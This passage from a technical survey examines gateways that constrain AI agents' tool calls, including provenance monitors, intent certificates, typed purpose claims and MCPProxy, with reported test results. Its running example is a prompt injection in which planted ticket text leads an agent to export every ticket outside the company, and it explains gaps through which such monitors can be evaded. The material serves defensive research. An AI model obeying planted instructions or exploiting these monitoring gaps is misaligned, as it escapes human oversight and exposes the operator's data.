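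A resource can also change between the agent's own requests, after it reads something in one call and before it relies on it in the next. Lilienthal and Hong (2025), in *Mind the Gap: Time-of-Check to Time-of-Use Vulnerabilities in LLM-Enabled Agents*, examined 66 tasks from AgentDojo, a set of simulated banking, chat, travel and office jobs. They judged 56 of these vulnerable to such a change. As defences, they rewrote the user's prompts, monitored for risky pairs of calls, and fused such pairs into single tools. Together these cut the share of runs with a vulnerable sequence from 12% to 8%, a difference of only about three tasks if each ran once. Fusing reduced the average time between the paired calls from 1.77 to 0.08 seconds.

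Their automatic detector found only 25% of the vulnerable sequences in the benchmark's model solutions and 14% of those in the agent's own plans, probably because it saw only the tool descriptions and not the user's request. There is little evidence on this problem in general. The survey *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026) lists only two papers on it, one by Lilienthal and Hong and the other a study of browser agents.

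### When the agent chooses the resource

All five steps can succeed on a resource the user never meant. In the "cancel my job" case, the agent picked the most similar name from a computing cluster's own list, so the job existed and had an exact identifier. Anthropic objects that the user may have meant another job and that this one could have belonged to somebody else.

Looking up the job's owner would stop the deletion if the job belonged to somebody else, but not if the user had two jobs with similar names. Checking where the identifier came from wouldn't help much either. Anthropic's judge model doesn't receive tool results, so it can't check whether the agent took an identifier from a listing or made it up. Anthropic accepts this limitation to keep planted text away from the judge. But even a gateway that could trace the identifier to the cluster's own listing couldn't confirm that it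 was the right one, because the listing also contained every other job.

Palumbo and colleagues address this problem with a monitor that runs outside the model. It records every message, tool request and result, along with the earlier events each could have depended on. Its rules are written in Datalog, a logic language that derives new facts from known ones, and they can trace the origin, or provenance, of each argument. If an action would change something, the rules allow the target if the user supplied it or it appears in a record that the operator maintains.

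That rule is too strict for a request such as "delete the largest file". The user has given no file name, so the agent has to list the files and choose one. If the policy refused every name from a listing, it would block the task. If it accepted every name from a listing, the agent could delete any file on it. The policy therefore takes the selection rule from the user's request and repeats the selection itself. Suppose the listing is:

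| File | Size |
|---|---|
| `contract.docx` | 1 MB |
| `report.pdf` | 2 MB |
| `backup.zip` | 900 MB |

The monitor determines that the user wants the file with the largest value in the size column, works out that this is `backup.zip`, and allows the deletion only if the argument matches that name. All three file names come from the same source, but only one is correct. The decision does not depend on the model's reason for choosing the file.

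On its own, this rule has a loophole, because any listing in the conversation that selects the target satisfies it. After deleting `backup.zip`, the agent could list the files again and then delete `report.pdf`, which would now be the largest. A search that returned only an attacker's record would also select that record. Palumbo and colleagues therefore add a second rule, which refuses the request if any listing in the conversation selects a different record. This rule occasionally refuses a request needlessly. If someone uploads a larger file between two accurate listings, the listings will select different files, and the agent can't delete either one.

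The same method would suit "cancel my job". The user's only criterion is that the job belongs to them. A gateway could list the signed-in user's jobs and, if there is exactly one, require the agent's argument to match it. If there were several, the gateway would have to ask which one to cancel. The agent chose a job by similarity of names, a criterion that nothing in the request supports.

### What the recomputing policy achieved

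Palumbo and colleagues tested their policy on AgentDojo with an agent built on GPT-4o, an older model. They ran 97 ordinary tasks and 949 attacks, five times each. In the results below, every version of the agent received the user's request again after each batch of tool results, which is itself a mild defence.

| Added defence | Attacks scored as successful | Successful attacks, not counting blocked calls | Tasks completed without attack | Tasks completed under attack |
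|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 14.1% | 14.1% | 83.7% | 72.5% |
| A model picks the permitted tools in advance | 3.1% | 3.1% | 73.4% | 69.5% |
| No consequential action after reading untrusted text | 0.6% | 0.3% | 33.2% | 34.4% |
| Provenance policy with recomputed targets | 0.9% | 0.2% | 62.5% | 63.8% |

The benchmark counts some attacks as successful when the agent only attempts the forbidden call, so the second column of figures leaves out attacks whose calls the monitor blocked. The few attacks that remained under the provenance policy succeeded when the agent recommended the attacker's hotel in its final answer, which needed no tool.

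The provenance policy let the agent complete nearly twice as many tasks as the blanket ban on acting after untrusted text, with about the same security. But even without an attack, the agent completed about a quarter fewer tasks than it would have without the policy. The monitor refused at least one request in 151 of the 485 runs without an attack, and the agent finished the task in only 36 of those 151. These figures are for the whole policy, so they don't show how much recomputing targets contributed to the benefit or to the lost tasks.

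One failure shows how much recomputing depends on the programmed criteria. A user wanted the highest-rated Paris hotel under a price ceiling, and planted text asked for the most expensive hotel on the same dates. The most expensive hotel was in the trusted catalogue, and the policy had no rule for comparing prices or ratings, so it allowed the booking. This happened in three attacked runs, all without the repeated request.

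The loss of completed tasks may depend on the setting. In simulated airline and retail customer service, with three newer models and no attacker, a different set of rules raised the average success rate from 74.7% to 81.5% for airline tasks and from 86.3% to 87.4% for retail tasks. Many of the blocked requests contained ordinary mistakes about the target or the terms, such as a refund to the wrong payment method, and the agent often corrected itself after the refusal. The monitor's decisions typically took less than a millisecond.

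### Stopping request C

Request C is a search, so it would pass the AgentDojo version of this policy. Palumbo and colleagues exempt reads from the check on targets because reads change nothing. At the ticket company, though, a search puts suppliers' bank details into the agent's context and perhaps into a summary for someone in customer support. A policy for this company has to cover what a request discloses as well as what it changes.

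Extending the provenance rule to reads wouldn't be enough. The user typed "refund tickets", which describes both queues but isn't the name of either. If the gateway accepted any name in the company's official list of queues, it would also accept `supply-refunds`, which is on the list.

Comparing owners works better. The login system lists the user under customer support, the ticket system assigns queue 2046 to supply chain, and the gateway holds the request because the two departments differ. The stated purpose is accurate, but it doesn't count in the request's favor.

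Now suppose the user is a manager with access to both units. The owner check correctly lets her search either queue, so it no longer catches the model's mistake. The company could record that "refund tickets", typed in the support tool, means queue 1183, and the gateway could require the resolved identifier to match. But this fixed record would also block her when she does want the suppliers' refunds. To distinguish the two cases, the gateway needs a list of the resources that this particular request justifies. An intent certificate, a short-lived record on the server, would contain that list.

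## Deriving the permitted purpose from the user's request

The gateway can work out what the user's message justifies before the agent reads anything else, instead of asking the agent to give a reason for running a tool. In the ticket example, the message is "Summarise the November refund tickets". The sentence that prompts request B is inside one of the tickets, so it can't affect what the gateway has already worked out.

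Zhu and Wang store the result in an intent certificate, which lists the actions, resources and limits that the request justifies. The gateway derives the certificate from the signed-in user's message and from trusted details of the request, such as which application sent it. Attachments, web pages, tool results, the agent's earlier replies and its long-term memory can help the agent plan but can't add anything to the certificate. "Intent" here means only what the user's words ask for, not what the user privately wanted.

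*Contextual Agent Security* (2025) proposed generating a policy for each task from trusted context alone. *Beyond OAuth* (2026) treats the user's task as the authorisation itself, covering both the operation and the things it operates on. These designs depend on the message really coming from the user, so the gateway in *aiAuthZ* (2026) checks that every user message is signed with a key the agent can't read.

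### A certificate for the refund summary

Here is a certificate for the example, modelled on a sample by Zhu and Wang, with invented values:

```json
{
  "id": "intent_0417",
  "requestHash": "sha256:...",
  "subjectBinding": { "actorId": "dana@company.example",
                      "appId": "support-agent",
                      "messageId": "msg_8821" },
  "intentClasses": ["read", "summarize"],
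  "deniedIntentClasses": ["create", "update", "delete",
                          "export", "admin"],
  "resourceBounds": { "queues": [1183],
                      "from": "2025-11-01", "to": "2025-11-30" },
  "effectBounds": { "maxRisk": "low", "allowExport": false,
                    "allowMutation": false },
  "confidence": 0.92,
  "maxRoutingOutcome": "execute",
  "issuedAt": "2025-12-01T09:00:00Z",
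  "expiresAt": "2025-12-01T09:05:00Z"
}
```

The `requestHash`, a fingerprint of the message, and the `subjectBinding` together tie the certificate to one user, one application and one message, so nobody can reuse it for another request. The certificate expires after five minutes, as in Zhu and Wang's sample. A complete certificate also records the versions of the access policy and the tool list, and whether a rule, a model, a step in the product or a person produced it.

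The intent classes are broad kinds of action. Zhu and Wang define ten, shown here with invented examples:

| Class | Example | What the certificate can permit |
|---|---|---|
| `read` | "Show me ticket 5120" | Reading within the limits |
| `summarize` | "Summarise the November refund tickets" | Reading and condensing, with no changes or exports |
| `transform` | "Sort these complaints into categories" | Computation only; any change becomes a draft |
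| `create` | "Open a ticket for this call" | A narrow draft, or immediate creation if the risk is low |
| `update` | "Close ticket 5120" | A draft change to the named record |
| `delete` | "Delete ticket 5120, it's a duplicate" | Deleting a few named records, after review |
| `export` | "Download the November tickets" | An export with explicit limits, after review |
| `delegate` | "Assign these to Sam" | Assigning or sending to a named person, after review |
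| `admin` | "Give Sam access to this queue" | Changing settings or permissions, after strict review |
| `unknown` | "Sort out the refunds" | Very few tools, a question to the user, or drafts only |

Before the agent plans anything, the gateway shortens the agent's list of tools. It first removes the tools that static policy forbids, then those that the certificate doesn't justify. In the example, the second step removes the export tool, leaving only tools for searching and reading.

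Hiding a tool doesn't stop an agent from naming it, and the agent can also misuse a tool that remains visible. Zhu and Wang gave three models 54 attack tasks each. With the full list of tools, the models proposed something unsafe in 50% to 93% of tasks, and with the shortened list they still did so in 44% to 70%. The gateway therefore also tests each request for consistency with the certificate. For a tool *t*, a payload *x* and an estimated effect *ê*, all of these must hold:

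- Class(*t*) ⊆ *I*⁺ and Class(*t*) ∩ *I*⁻ = ∅: the certificate permits every class of action the tool performs and denies none of them.
- *B*<sub>R</sub>(*x*) = 1: the resources in the payload are within the resource limits.
- *B*<sub>E</sub>(*ê*) = 1: the estimated effect is within the effect limits.

The three requests from the example give these results:

| | Request A | Request B | Request C |
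|---|---|---|---|
| Tool class | `read`: permitted | `export`: denied | `read`: permitted |
| Resources | Queue 1183, November: within limits | All 52,000 tickets: outside | Queue 2046: outside |
| Effect | Reads tickets: within limits | Sends data outside the company: outside | Reads tickets: within limits |
| Result | Execute | Deny | Deny |

Request C fails only because of its resources. Zhu and Wang's design returns the refusal with a code for a payload that exceeds its limits, which means the same call would fail again. The agent could then find its mistake and search `support-refunds`.

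The certificate also helps with the manager who has access to both business units. If she types "Summarise the November supplier refunds", the gateway can issue a certificate for queue 2046, and request C becomes legitimate. If she types only "refund tickets", the gateway can infer the queue from the page she typed it on, if the application reports the page reliably, or ask her which queue she means.

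None of these tests uses the agent's stated purpose. A request to close 30 apparent duplicates to "tidy up refund tickets" would fail, however reasonable that purpose sounded, because the certificate denies the `update` class.

### From deny to execute

The gateway can deny a request, ask the user to clarify it, save the proposed action as a draft for a person to review, run a preflight, require confirmation, or execute the action. A preflight calculates what the action would affect and ties any later approval to that result and to the exact payload. The drafts and preflights come from OpenPort, an earlier protocol for agent gateways (Zhu, Wang and colleagues, 2026, *OpenPort Protocol*).

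A request that fails the consistency test can only lead to a denial or a question. Zhu and Wang don't allow the gateway to save it as a draft, because a draft takes up a reviewer's time and can put misleading content in front of the person who approves it.

A request that passes can still need review. The certificate includes a confidence score for the interpretation of the user's message. Low confidence leads to a question, and medium confidence to a draft or preflight. The gateway executes a request immediately only if confidence is high and the action is low-risk. If it can't put a limit on what a tool would do, it denies the request or asks the user.

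### Two guarantees, one of them conditional

Zhu and Wang's first guarantee is that a certificate can never give the agent more authority than static policy does. It follows from the way the gateway combines the two:

accepted with a certificate ⇒ allowed by static policy

An intent derived from the user's message can only narrow the agent's authority, even if the classifier (the rule or model that interprets the message) is wrong or under an attacker's control.

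In the ticket example, this guarantee offers little protection because static policy already allows requests B and C. If the classifier produced a certificate for reading and exporting any ticket in any queue, request C would run. Request B would go to a person for review because exports are high-risk, but the certificate would no longer be a reason to refuse it. Such broad credentials are common. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) describes a type of access token for code repositories that gives an agent about 40 tools, including 16 that can make changes, across all the repositories its user can access.

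The second guarantee is the one the company needs: the agent can execute only what the user's request justifies. It holds under three conditions.

First, the certificate must be faithful, meaning that no field is broader than the message justifies. Zhu and Wang define this by comparison with a reference envelope, an independent and correct account of what the message justifies. They wrote the reference envelopes for their tests themselves, but in daily use nobody writes one for each message, so a company can check faithfulness only on samples.

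Second, the gateway must not underestimate a tool's effects, which it estimates from the tool's schema, its maker's declaration, or a preflight. Suppose the ticket search also sends each query and its results to an outside translation service. If the maker declares the tool as a simple read, the gateway will approve the search without checking the disclosure.

Third, every request must go through the gateway. If the agent can also run shell commands and finds the database password in a configuration file, it can read any ticket without a certificate.

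### What the tests measured

Zhu and Wang first tested the gateway on 176 synthetic tasks, of which 102 were legitimate and 74 involved an attack or an ambiguous request. Supplying the correct certificates cut the failure rate on those 74 tasks from 100% to zero. The researchers counted a task as a failure if the agent could even see a high-risk tool that the task didn't justify, and a gateway without certificates normally shows such tools. Neither version of the gateway completed an unsafe action, so the test shows that the gateway applies correct certificates properly, but not that certificates prevented any harm.

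The end-to-end trials are more realistic because models wrote the certificates and chose the tool calls. Three older open-weight models, GPT-OSS-120B, Llama-3.3-70B and Qwen3-Next-80B, each attempted 34 tasks three times, for a total of 306 trials. In the 198 trials with an attack or an ambiguous request, the gateway completed no unsafe action, but it accepted 40 requests that the reference envelope didn't justify, all as drafts that it never executed. Zhu and Wang call this unsafe accepted authority, and its rate ranged from 9.09% for Llama to 27.27% for Qwen. In 24 of the 40 cases, the payload went beyond what the user had asked to create, and the certificate's limits were missing or too weak to catch it. In the other 16, deceptive tool descriptions led to drafts that looked like ordinary new records.

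The absence of unsafe executions is less impressive because the gateway also completed none of the 108 legitimate trials. It turned 36 of them into drafts for review, and 67 failed because the agent's call was malformed. Zhu and Wang didn't test the same models without certificates, so the trials can't show how much of the result was due to the certificates and how much to OpenPort turning risky changes into drafts.

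They also calculated what stricter checking of the certificates would have done in the recorded trials:

| Check on the certificate | Unsafe drafts accepted, of 198 | Legitimate drafts produced, of 108 |
|---|---|---|
| As run | 40 | 36 |
| Strict validation of limits | 15 | 15 |
| Strict validation, with limits also converted to a standard form | 0 | 15 |

Rules strict enough to remove every unsafe draft would also have removed 21 of the 36 legitimate ones. The actual number could be different, since Zhu and Wang wrote the stricter rules after studying the failures and didn't run the models again.

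A smaller set of 12 tasks, modelled on four existing benchmarks, gave similar results, with 5 unsafe drafts in 24 trials and no unsafe executions. All of these tests are small and use synthetic data, and the gateway's designers also wrote the tasks and the correct answers. Both authors are affiliated with Accentrust, which maintains OpenPort with the protocol's authors, so an independent test would be valuable.

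### Extracting the task from a conversation

A certificate is simplest when it covers a single message. In a longer conversation, the user may name the queue in one message, the month in another and the action in a third. *Hybrid Inspection and Task-Based Access Control in Zero-Trust Agentic AI* (El Helou, Ryder and colleagues, 2026) handles this in two stages. First, a model condenses the conversation up to the first tool call into a single request. Then the same model or another one uses that request and the tool's name and description to decide whether the tool is appropriate.

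The instructions for the first stage are meant to keep the agent's ideas out of the user's task. If the agent offers to do something extra and the user replies only "thanks", the extra step doesn't count as part of the task. The model may use the agent's messages only to work out what a word such as "it" refers to, or what the user has confirmed.

El Helou and colleagues at Cisco tested four models on synthetic conversations based on tools from 12 business systems. In some conversations in the hardest set, they had secretly instructed the agent to call an irrelevant tool. In one, the user wanted to remove a file from a code repository. The agent asked for the "thread ID" of a related notification, the user supplied one, and the agent dismissed the notification instead of removing the file.

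| Test set | Irrelevant tools wrongly allowed | Relevant tools wrongly blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Single explicit tasks | 2% to 8% | 0% to 2% |
| Longer conversations, scripted | 2% to 12% | 0% to 4% |
| Longer conversations between simulated users and agents | 10% to 20% | 1% to 7% |

Each range covers the four models. In the last row, Claude Sonnet 4.6 wrongly allowed the smallest share of irrelevant tools, 10%, but it also blocked 7% of the relevant ones. About 45% of the test cases had an irrelevant tool, far more than a company would expect in normal use. If 1% of 10,000 requests were illegitimate, a check with these error rates would block 90 of the 100 illegitimate requests and 693 of the 9,900 legitimate ones, so only about one in nine blocked requests would be illegitimate.

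The second stage is also much less precise than a certificate. It isn't given the payload, so it can't distinguish request A from request C, which use the same search tool. It might even allow request B, because it is instructed to reject a tool only if it is "completely unrelated" to the task, and a model could easily classify exporting tickets as helpful for summarising them. El Helou and colleagues' separate checks on the agent program wouldn't stop request B either, because they verify that the program runs exactly the call the model wrote, and the model did write the export.

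### When the misreading moves upstream

If a model writes the certificate or extracts the task, the gateway relies on one model's interpretation to control another. The first model may misread the user's request before the agent acts on it. Cloudflare's *The Agent Access Model* makes the related objection that an attacker can use the same text to manipulate the agent and influence the inferred intent.

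Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues (2026) answer the charge of circularity in *Sapien*. Sapien, developed mainly at Google, has a model write a policy for each task and a program enforce it. The policy writer sees only the user's prompt and the tools' documentation, so text planted in a ticket or an email can't reach it. Its job is also much narrower than the agent's, because it only translates one request into rules, whereas the agent works through many steps in which it can drift from the goal or improvise.

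Results from Tiffany and colleagues suggest that a model can do this job fairly well. They assumed that an attacker had complete control of the agent and checked whether the policy would still permit the attack. The policies ruled out 93% to 95% of attacks on AgentDojo and 62% to 85% on Toolathlon, a benchmark with longer tasks. The agents still completed nearly as many tasks as they did without a policy.

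Isolation doesn't make the policy writer's input entirely safe. A user might paste a customer's complaint into the message and type "deal with this", which puts the customer's words inside the trusted text. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) notes that a manipulated prompt can lead to broader permissions than the user intended. Whoever writes a tool's description can also put misleading text in the documentation. El Helou and colleagues' extractor is more exposed than the other two designs because it also reads the agent's replies, which planted text may have influenced. It is instructed not to treat those replies as the user's wishes, but it is a model and may not follow that instruction.

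Isolation also doesn't prevent honest misreadings. If the user's words are ambiguous, the policy writer and the agent may misunderstand them in the same way, especially if they are the same model. Suppose both take "refund tickets" to mean the suppliers' queue. The certificate then lists queue 2046, and request C passes the test. This match between certificate and request adds no more assurance than a match between a request's stated purpose and its own payload.

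The rule that intent can only narrow authority doesn't help here either, because static policy allows searches of both queues. *Agenra* (2026) presents a formally verified core for this kind of monitor and notes that a monitor can't enforce a requirement missing from its policy. The paper's proofs apply only once somebody has interpreted the request correctly.

Models also tend to be worst at identifying resources, the part of the certificate that request C depends on. When Zhu and Wang had their three models write certificates for 55 synthetic tasks, the models chose the correct intent classes (such as reading records) in 73% to 85% of cases but identified the correct resources (such as which records to read) in only 18% to 58%. GPT-OSS-120B, which did best on resources, also marked 86% of high-risk requests for immediate execution. The gateway overrides that mark, but it has no equally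 simple way to correct a certificate that names the wrong queue.

For this reason, the resource limits should come from something other than a model where possible. If the user opens the refund queue and presses a "Summarise" button, the product supplies the queue number. Rules can also help. On the 176-task set, a simple rule-based classifier got the resource limits right in 90% of tasks, and a version that also used information from the product's workflow got them right in 99%. These figures aren't directly comparable with those for the models, because the tasks were different and came from templates written by the same authors.

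### Vague requests

Some messages don't contain enough information for a narrow certificate. "Sort out the refund tickets" could mean summarising, assigning, answering or closing them. Zhu and Wang would put such a message in the `unknown` class, offer the agent very few tools and ask the user what they want.

Sapien, by Tiffany and colleagues, instead accepts that a vague prompt produces a wide policy, which may permit harmful calls, and relies on a separate mechanism to ask the user about unusual or risky actions. This interrupts the user less often, but it gives the least protection when a vague prompt forces the agent to guess.

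Whether the gateway guesses the user's meaning or asks can depend on how much harm a wrong guess would do. For a summary, it could let the agent search any queue that belongs to the user's own department, since a misunderstanding would waste only a few minutes. For a deletion, it should ask the user. For the agent told to "clean up old branches", a certificate could have allowed it to list the branches but not delete any until the user had said which ones, and whether to include the copies on the shared server.

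Clear requests can be wrong too. If the user asks the agent to delete ticket 5120 but meant 5210, a faithful certificate permits the wrong deletion. Tiffany and colleagues explicitly exclude this problem, because the policy is meant to keep the agent to what the user wrote.

### Tasks that change along the way

After reading the summary, the user might write "Now close the duplicates". The first certificate doesn't cover this, and extending it would give the agent read, search and change permissions for tickets at the same time. Zhu and Wang prefer to issue a new certificate for each step. They let certificates expire after a set time, after a number of turns or once the permitted action is complete, so that old permissions don't accumulate in a long conversation.

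But the new message doesn't specify which tickets are duplicates. Only the agent's own list does, and planted text may have affected it. Under Zhu and Wang's rule, a certificate for reading may be used to find candidates, but a certificate for changing, deleting or exporting can be issued only after the user has confirmed the actual targets. In the example, the gateway would show the user the ticket numbers and titles from the ticket system, then issue an `update` certificate for the tickets the user selected.

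Asking the user at every step would make the agent tedious to use, and sometimes the user has already given a rule for choosing the target. Tiffany and colleagues use the request "refund the person who sent me money last week". Sapien doesn't know the recipient when it writes the policy, but it can require the agent to read the list of transactions first, and then allow a payment only to a sender and for an amount listed in last week's entries. The list can determine who receives the money, but it can't change the rule. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) similarly says that evidence found during the task may identify the recipient the user authorised but doesn't authorise additional ones.

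The line is harder to maintain when the user hands over part of the decision, as in "complete the items on my to-do list". Sapien leaves a gap in the policy for these items and fills it only after the agent has fetched the list, so the agent doesn't get blanket permission in advance. This is reasonable for a list that only the user can edit. If the support user wrote "do whatever the customers ask in these tickets", customers, including the one who asked for the entire archive, would write the text that fills the gap.

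## Comparing the model's claims with facts held by the server

An intent certificate lets a gateway stop requests B and C without reading their stated purpose. In *Explanation-Bound Tool Execution for AI Agents*, written after their paper on certificates, Zhu and Wang still ask the model for its purpose, but have it broken down into typed claims, which are statements in fixed fields that a program can check. The gateway compares each claim with a fact held by the server.

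### From a sentence to fields

A program can't do much with "summarise refund tickets", because the sentence doesn't say which queue the agent will search, how many tickets it will read or where the result will go. A set of typed claims gives each of these separately. Here is one for request A, shortened and with invented values:

```json
{
  "intentClasses": ["read", "summarize"],
  "intentSummary": "Summarise refund tickets.",
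  "selectedTool": "search_tickets",
  "expectedEffect": { "operation": "read",
                      "resourceType": "ticket_queue",
                      "resourceIds": ["support-refunds"],
                      "maxRecords": 250 },
  "riskTier": "low",
  "uncertainty": { "level": "low", "reasonCodes": [] },
  "untrustedContextDependencies": []
}
```

The gateway treats all of this as unproven and compares it field by field:

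| Claim | What the gateway compares it with | If they disagree |
|---|---|---|
| Intent class | The classes in the intent certificate | Deny |
| Tool | The tool in the request, and the server's list of tools eligible for the task | Deny |
| Operation and resource | The payload and the certificate | Deny |
| Number of records, sum of money, data fields | The payload and the certificate | Deny; review if the claim leaves it out |
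| Destination | The payload | Deny; review if the claim leaves it out |
| Policy rules that apply | The current access policy | Deny; review if the claim leaves them out |
| Risk | The risk level in the company's own register of tools | Review if the claim is too low |
| Untrusted sources | The server's record of the agent's current context | Deny |
| Uncertainty | Nothing | Review if the model declares it high |
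| Summary | Nothing | No effect |

The summary, formerly the purpose field, is the only part of the claim that no rule uses. It is still there for people to read.

The gateway can read the operation, resource and destination directly from the payload because the tool will act on it, even though the payload isn't a fact held by the server. The risk level comes from a register that the company maintains rather than from the tool maker's description, which an attacker may have written.

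The model must also return digests (short fingerprints) of the current certificate, policy and payload. If any digest is out of date, the gateway denies the request. An agent therefore can't reuse a claim that was true before the user's task changed.

### How the gateway reaches a decision

Each comparison has one of four results. A match means the claim agrees with the facts. A hard result is a contradiction about something that matters to the action, such as the wrong tool. A soft result is a weaker problem, such as an understated risk. The result is unknown if the server can't obtain the fact it needs.

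A match leads to "allow", a soft or unknown result to "review", and a hard result to "deny". Zhu and Wang put these outcomes in order of strictness:

Allow < Review < Deny

The strictest result among all the fields becomes the result of the claim check. If the tool is high-risk, the result is at least "review", even when every field matches. The gateway then combines the claim check with two other controls:

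final decision = strictest of (baseline, claim check, effect control)

The baseline is ordinary authorisation and routing. Effect control covers measures such as a preflight or a confirmation step. If the baseline and effect control both return "allow" but the claim check returns "review", the request goes to review. A single contradiction is enough to stop the request, whereas under a majority vote nine matching fields could outweigh one false destination.

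A claim therefore can't make the gateway more lenient, because adding an item to a list can't make the strictest item less strict. Even a perfect claim doesn't change the decision reached by the other controls.

The gateway sends a badly formatted claim to review, but it still compares the fields it can read, so an agent can't turn a denial into a review by adding a formatting error. Review never runs the tool. If a person later approves the request, the gateway has to look up all the facts again and repeat the whole calculation, because the certificate may have expired or the policy may have changed.

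Zhu and Wang also show that a request with a hard contradiction never executes if the gateway repeats the check at the moment of action and much the same conditions hold as for the certificate. One of those conditions is that the server's facts are correct. If the company's register wrongly lists the export tool as low-risk, a false claim of low risk will match it.

### The rule for numbers

For quantities such as the number of records or a sum of money, the claim has to lie between what the request would do and what the user's task justifies:

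payload ≤ claim ≤ certificate limit

Suppose the certificate for the refund summary also set a limit of 300 tickets, and the search tool took a maximum number of tickets as an argument.

| Payload | Claim | Certificate limit | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| 240 | 250 | 300 | Match |
| 240 | 200 | 300 | Deny: the claim understates the request |
| 240 | 400 | 300 | Deny: the claim exceeds the limit |
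| 240 | None | 300 | Review: the claim is incomplete |
| 52,000 | 52,000 | 300 | Deny: the claim is true, but both numbers exceed the limit |

The same rule applies to lists of data fields. If the agent asks for the date and amount of each refund, its claim must list at least those two fields and no field outside the certificate.

The third row is a legitimate search of 240 tickets that fails only because the model described it too broadly. For numbers, checking the claim can add refusals like this one, but it can't allow a request that the gateway would refuse if it compared the payload directly with the certificate limit. This is because whenever both inequalities hold, the payload is also within that limit.

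### Request B with two different claims

The model might describe request B as the summary that the user wanted, or it might describe the export truthfully.

| Field | Facts and payload | Claim that hides the export | Claim that admits the export |
|---|---|---|---|
| Intent class | Certificate: `read`, `summarize` | `read`, `summarize`: match | `export`: deny |
| Tool | Request: `export_tickets`; eligible: search and read tools | `search_tickets`: deny | `export_tickets`: deny, because it isn't eligible |
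| Operation | Payload: export; certificate: read | Read: deny | Export: deny |
| Resource | Payload: all queues; certificate: queue 1183 | Queue 1183: deny | All queues: deny |
| Number of tickets | Payload: 52,000; certificate: 300 | 240: deny | 52,000: deny |
| Destination | Payload: outside address; certificate: none | Left blank: review | Outside address: agrees with the payload, but the payload exceeds the certificate, so deny |
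| Risk | Register: high | Low: review | High: match, but a high-risk tool needs review |
| Untrusted sources | Customers' tickets | None: deny | Customers' tickets: match |

The gateway denies both versions. The model could not have gotten request B approved by making a different claim, because the request's operation, resource and number of tickets all exceed what the certificate allows.

The recorded reasons differ between the two versions. The first produces codes for a wrong tool and an omitted untrusted source, so an investigator can see that the agent misdescribed its own action. The second produces codes for an operation outside the certificate, which suggests that the agent accurately described an action nobody had asked for. A confused model could produce either pattern, so neither proves an attack.

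For request C, the claim would probably name the same wrong queue as the payload, so only the certificate would stop the search.

### What the tests measured

Zhu and Wang wrote 136 cases from eight kinds of task, such as exporting records or creating an appointment. Each kind has one correct case and 16 altered ones. In total, 96 cases contain a hard contradiction, 32 contain a softer problem and 8 are correct. The researchers ran all of them through the complete check and through three weaker versions:

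| What the gateway checks | Hard contradictions allowed, of 96 | Softer problems allowed, of 32 |
|---|---|---|
| That some free-text justification is present | 60 (62.5%) | 20 |
| That the claim has the required format | 55 (57.3%) | 5 |
| Also that the claim agrees with the payload | 35 (36.5%) | 5 |
| Everything, including the certificate, policy, risk and sources | 0 | 0 |

The free-text version accepts any non-empty text, so it stops a request only when the tool is high-risk. Three of the eight kinds of task need review for that reason, and the other five go through, which gives the figure of 62.5%. A different mix of tasks would change the figure, even with the same check. The figure also doesn't measure how well a person or a model could judge the text by reading it.

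The third row is more useful because it shows the common-source problem. Even in these simple cases, comparing the claim with the payload missed more than a third of the contradictions.

The zero in the last row shows that the program follows its own rules, because Zhu and Wang took the expected answers from the rule table it implements. They also wrote the cases, and they are affiliated with the company that maintains OpenPort. In a second test, they connected the checker to OpenPort, where every request it forwarded became a draft. The free-text version forwarded all 48 contradictory requests, the format check 44, the payload comparison 28 and the complete check none. The complete check took about a third of a millisecond or less in 95% of cases.

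In a third test, four hosted models wrote the claims. They received 12 synthetic tasks twice each, with feedback and one chance to repair the claim after each attempt. In further attempts, they had to repair claims that the researchers had broken on purpose. Of the 224 attempts, the current version of the checker allowed 56, sent 75 to review and denied 93.

The checker allowed none of the 64 attempts it should have denied. But it denied 93 attempts in total, so at least 29 of those should have passed or gone to review. Some of these may be failures to repair the broken claims. Feedback didn't help overall, since the checker's decision matched the expected one in 70 of 96 first attempts and in 65 of 96 after feedback.

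The models' task was easier than it would be in practice, because their prompt contained the server's facts and told them to describe the action truthfully, so they could often copy the right value. Even so, 43 of the 203 responses were not valid claims, and another 21 attempts failed because the provider returned an error. All of these went to review. When the researchers ran the current version of the checker on the saved claims, 56 decisions became stricter and none became more lenient.

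The last test used 12 attacks from the banking part of AgentDojo. The weaker versions of the check held all 12 for review because payment tools are high-risk, while the complete check denied them. This is an improvement, since a reviewer can approve a held request by mistake. But every claim in this test was true, and the complete check denied the requests by comparing the proposed action with the certificate. The test is therefore evidence that the certificate is useful, not that the claims are.

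Nobody has tested the check against attacks designed to defeat it. The tests also didn't include human reviewers, explanations from ordinary use, or the step in which an approved draft runs. Zhu and Wang have not released the code or the case-level data, so other researchers can't easily repeat the work.

### A simpler claim in MCPProxy

MCPProxy is a gateway for MCP servers. As its *Intent Declaration* explains, the agent claims a type for each tool call by making it through one of three wrappers, `call_tool_read`, `call_tool_write` or `call_tool_destructive`. A user can then set a code editor to approve reads automatically, ask about writes and always ask about destructive calls. The agent may add a reason of up to 1,000 characters, which MCPProxy keeps for the audit log.

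The proxy compares the agent's choice with the tool's annotations. These are optional labels the tool's maker uses to state, for example, that the tool only reads data (`readOnlyHint`) or can destroy data (`destructiveHint`).

| The agent calls the tool as | Marked read-only | Marked destructive | No annotation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read | Allow | Reject | Allow, trusting the agent |
| Write | Allow with a warning | Reject | Allow |
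| Destructive | Allow | Allow | Allow |

This strict mode is the default. If the owner turns it off, a mismatch produces only a warning. The bottom row is lenient because the user's editor should always ask about a destructive call, so an agent gains nothing by exaggerating the danger.

The gap is in the last column. If the ticket company's export tool has no annotations, the agent can send request B through `call_tool_read`, and the proxy has no annotation to check that choice against. The editor then approves the request automatically, and all 52,000 tickets leave the company without a person approving the export. Even with annotations, the proxy would have the same weaknesses as Google Cloud's read-only rule, which can't tell request A from request C and may let request B through.

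Model Context Protocol (2026) makes the opposite assumption, that a tool without annotations may change or destroy data. It also says that agent programs must not rely on annotations from servers they don't trust. Dumbris (2026), in *Deep Dive*, an article on MCPProxy's website, describes similar caution in the proxy, which recommends the `call_tool_write` wrapper for a tool without annotations. An earlier release wrongly recommended `call_tool_read` by default, which the developers have fixed. But the agent can ignore the recommendation, and the decision table still accepts a read.

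The same gap weakens another of MCPProxy's controls. A company can give an agent a token that permits only `call_tool_read`. According to the decision table, the agent could still use `call_tool_read` to call a deletion tool if the tool's maker hadn't annotated it, although Dumbris says that such an agent can't write or delete anything even if an attacker controls it.

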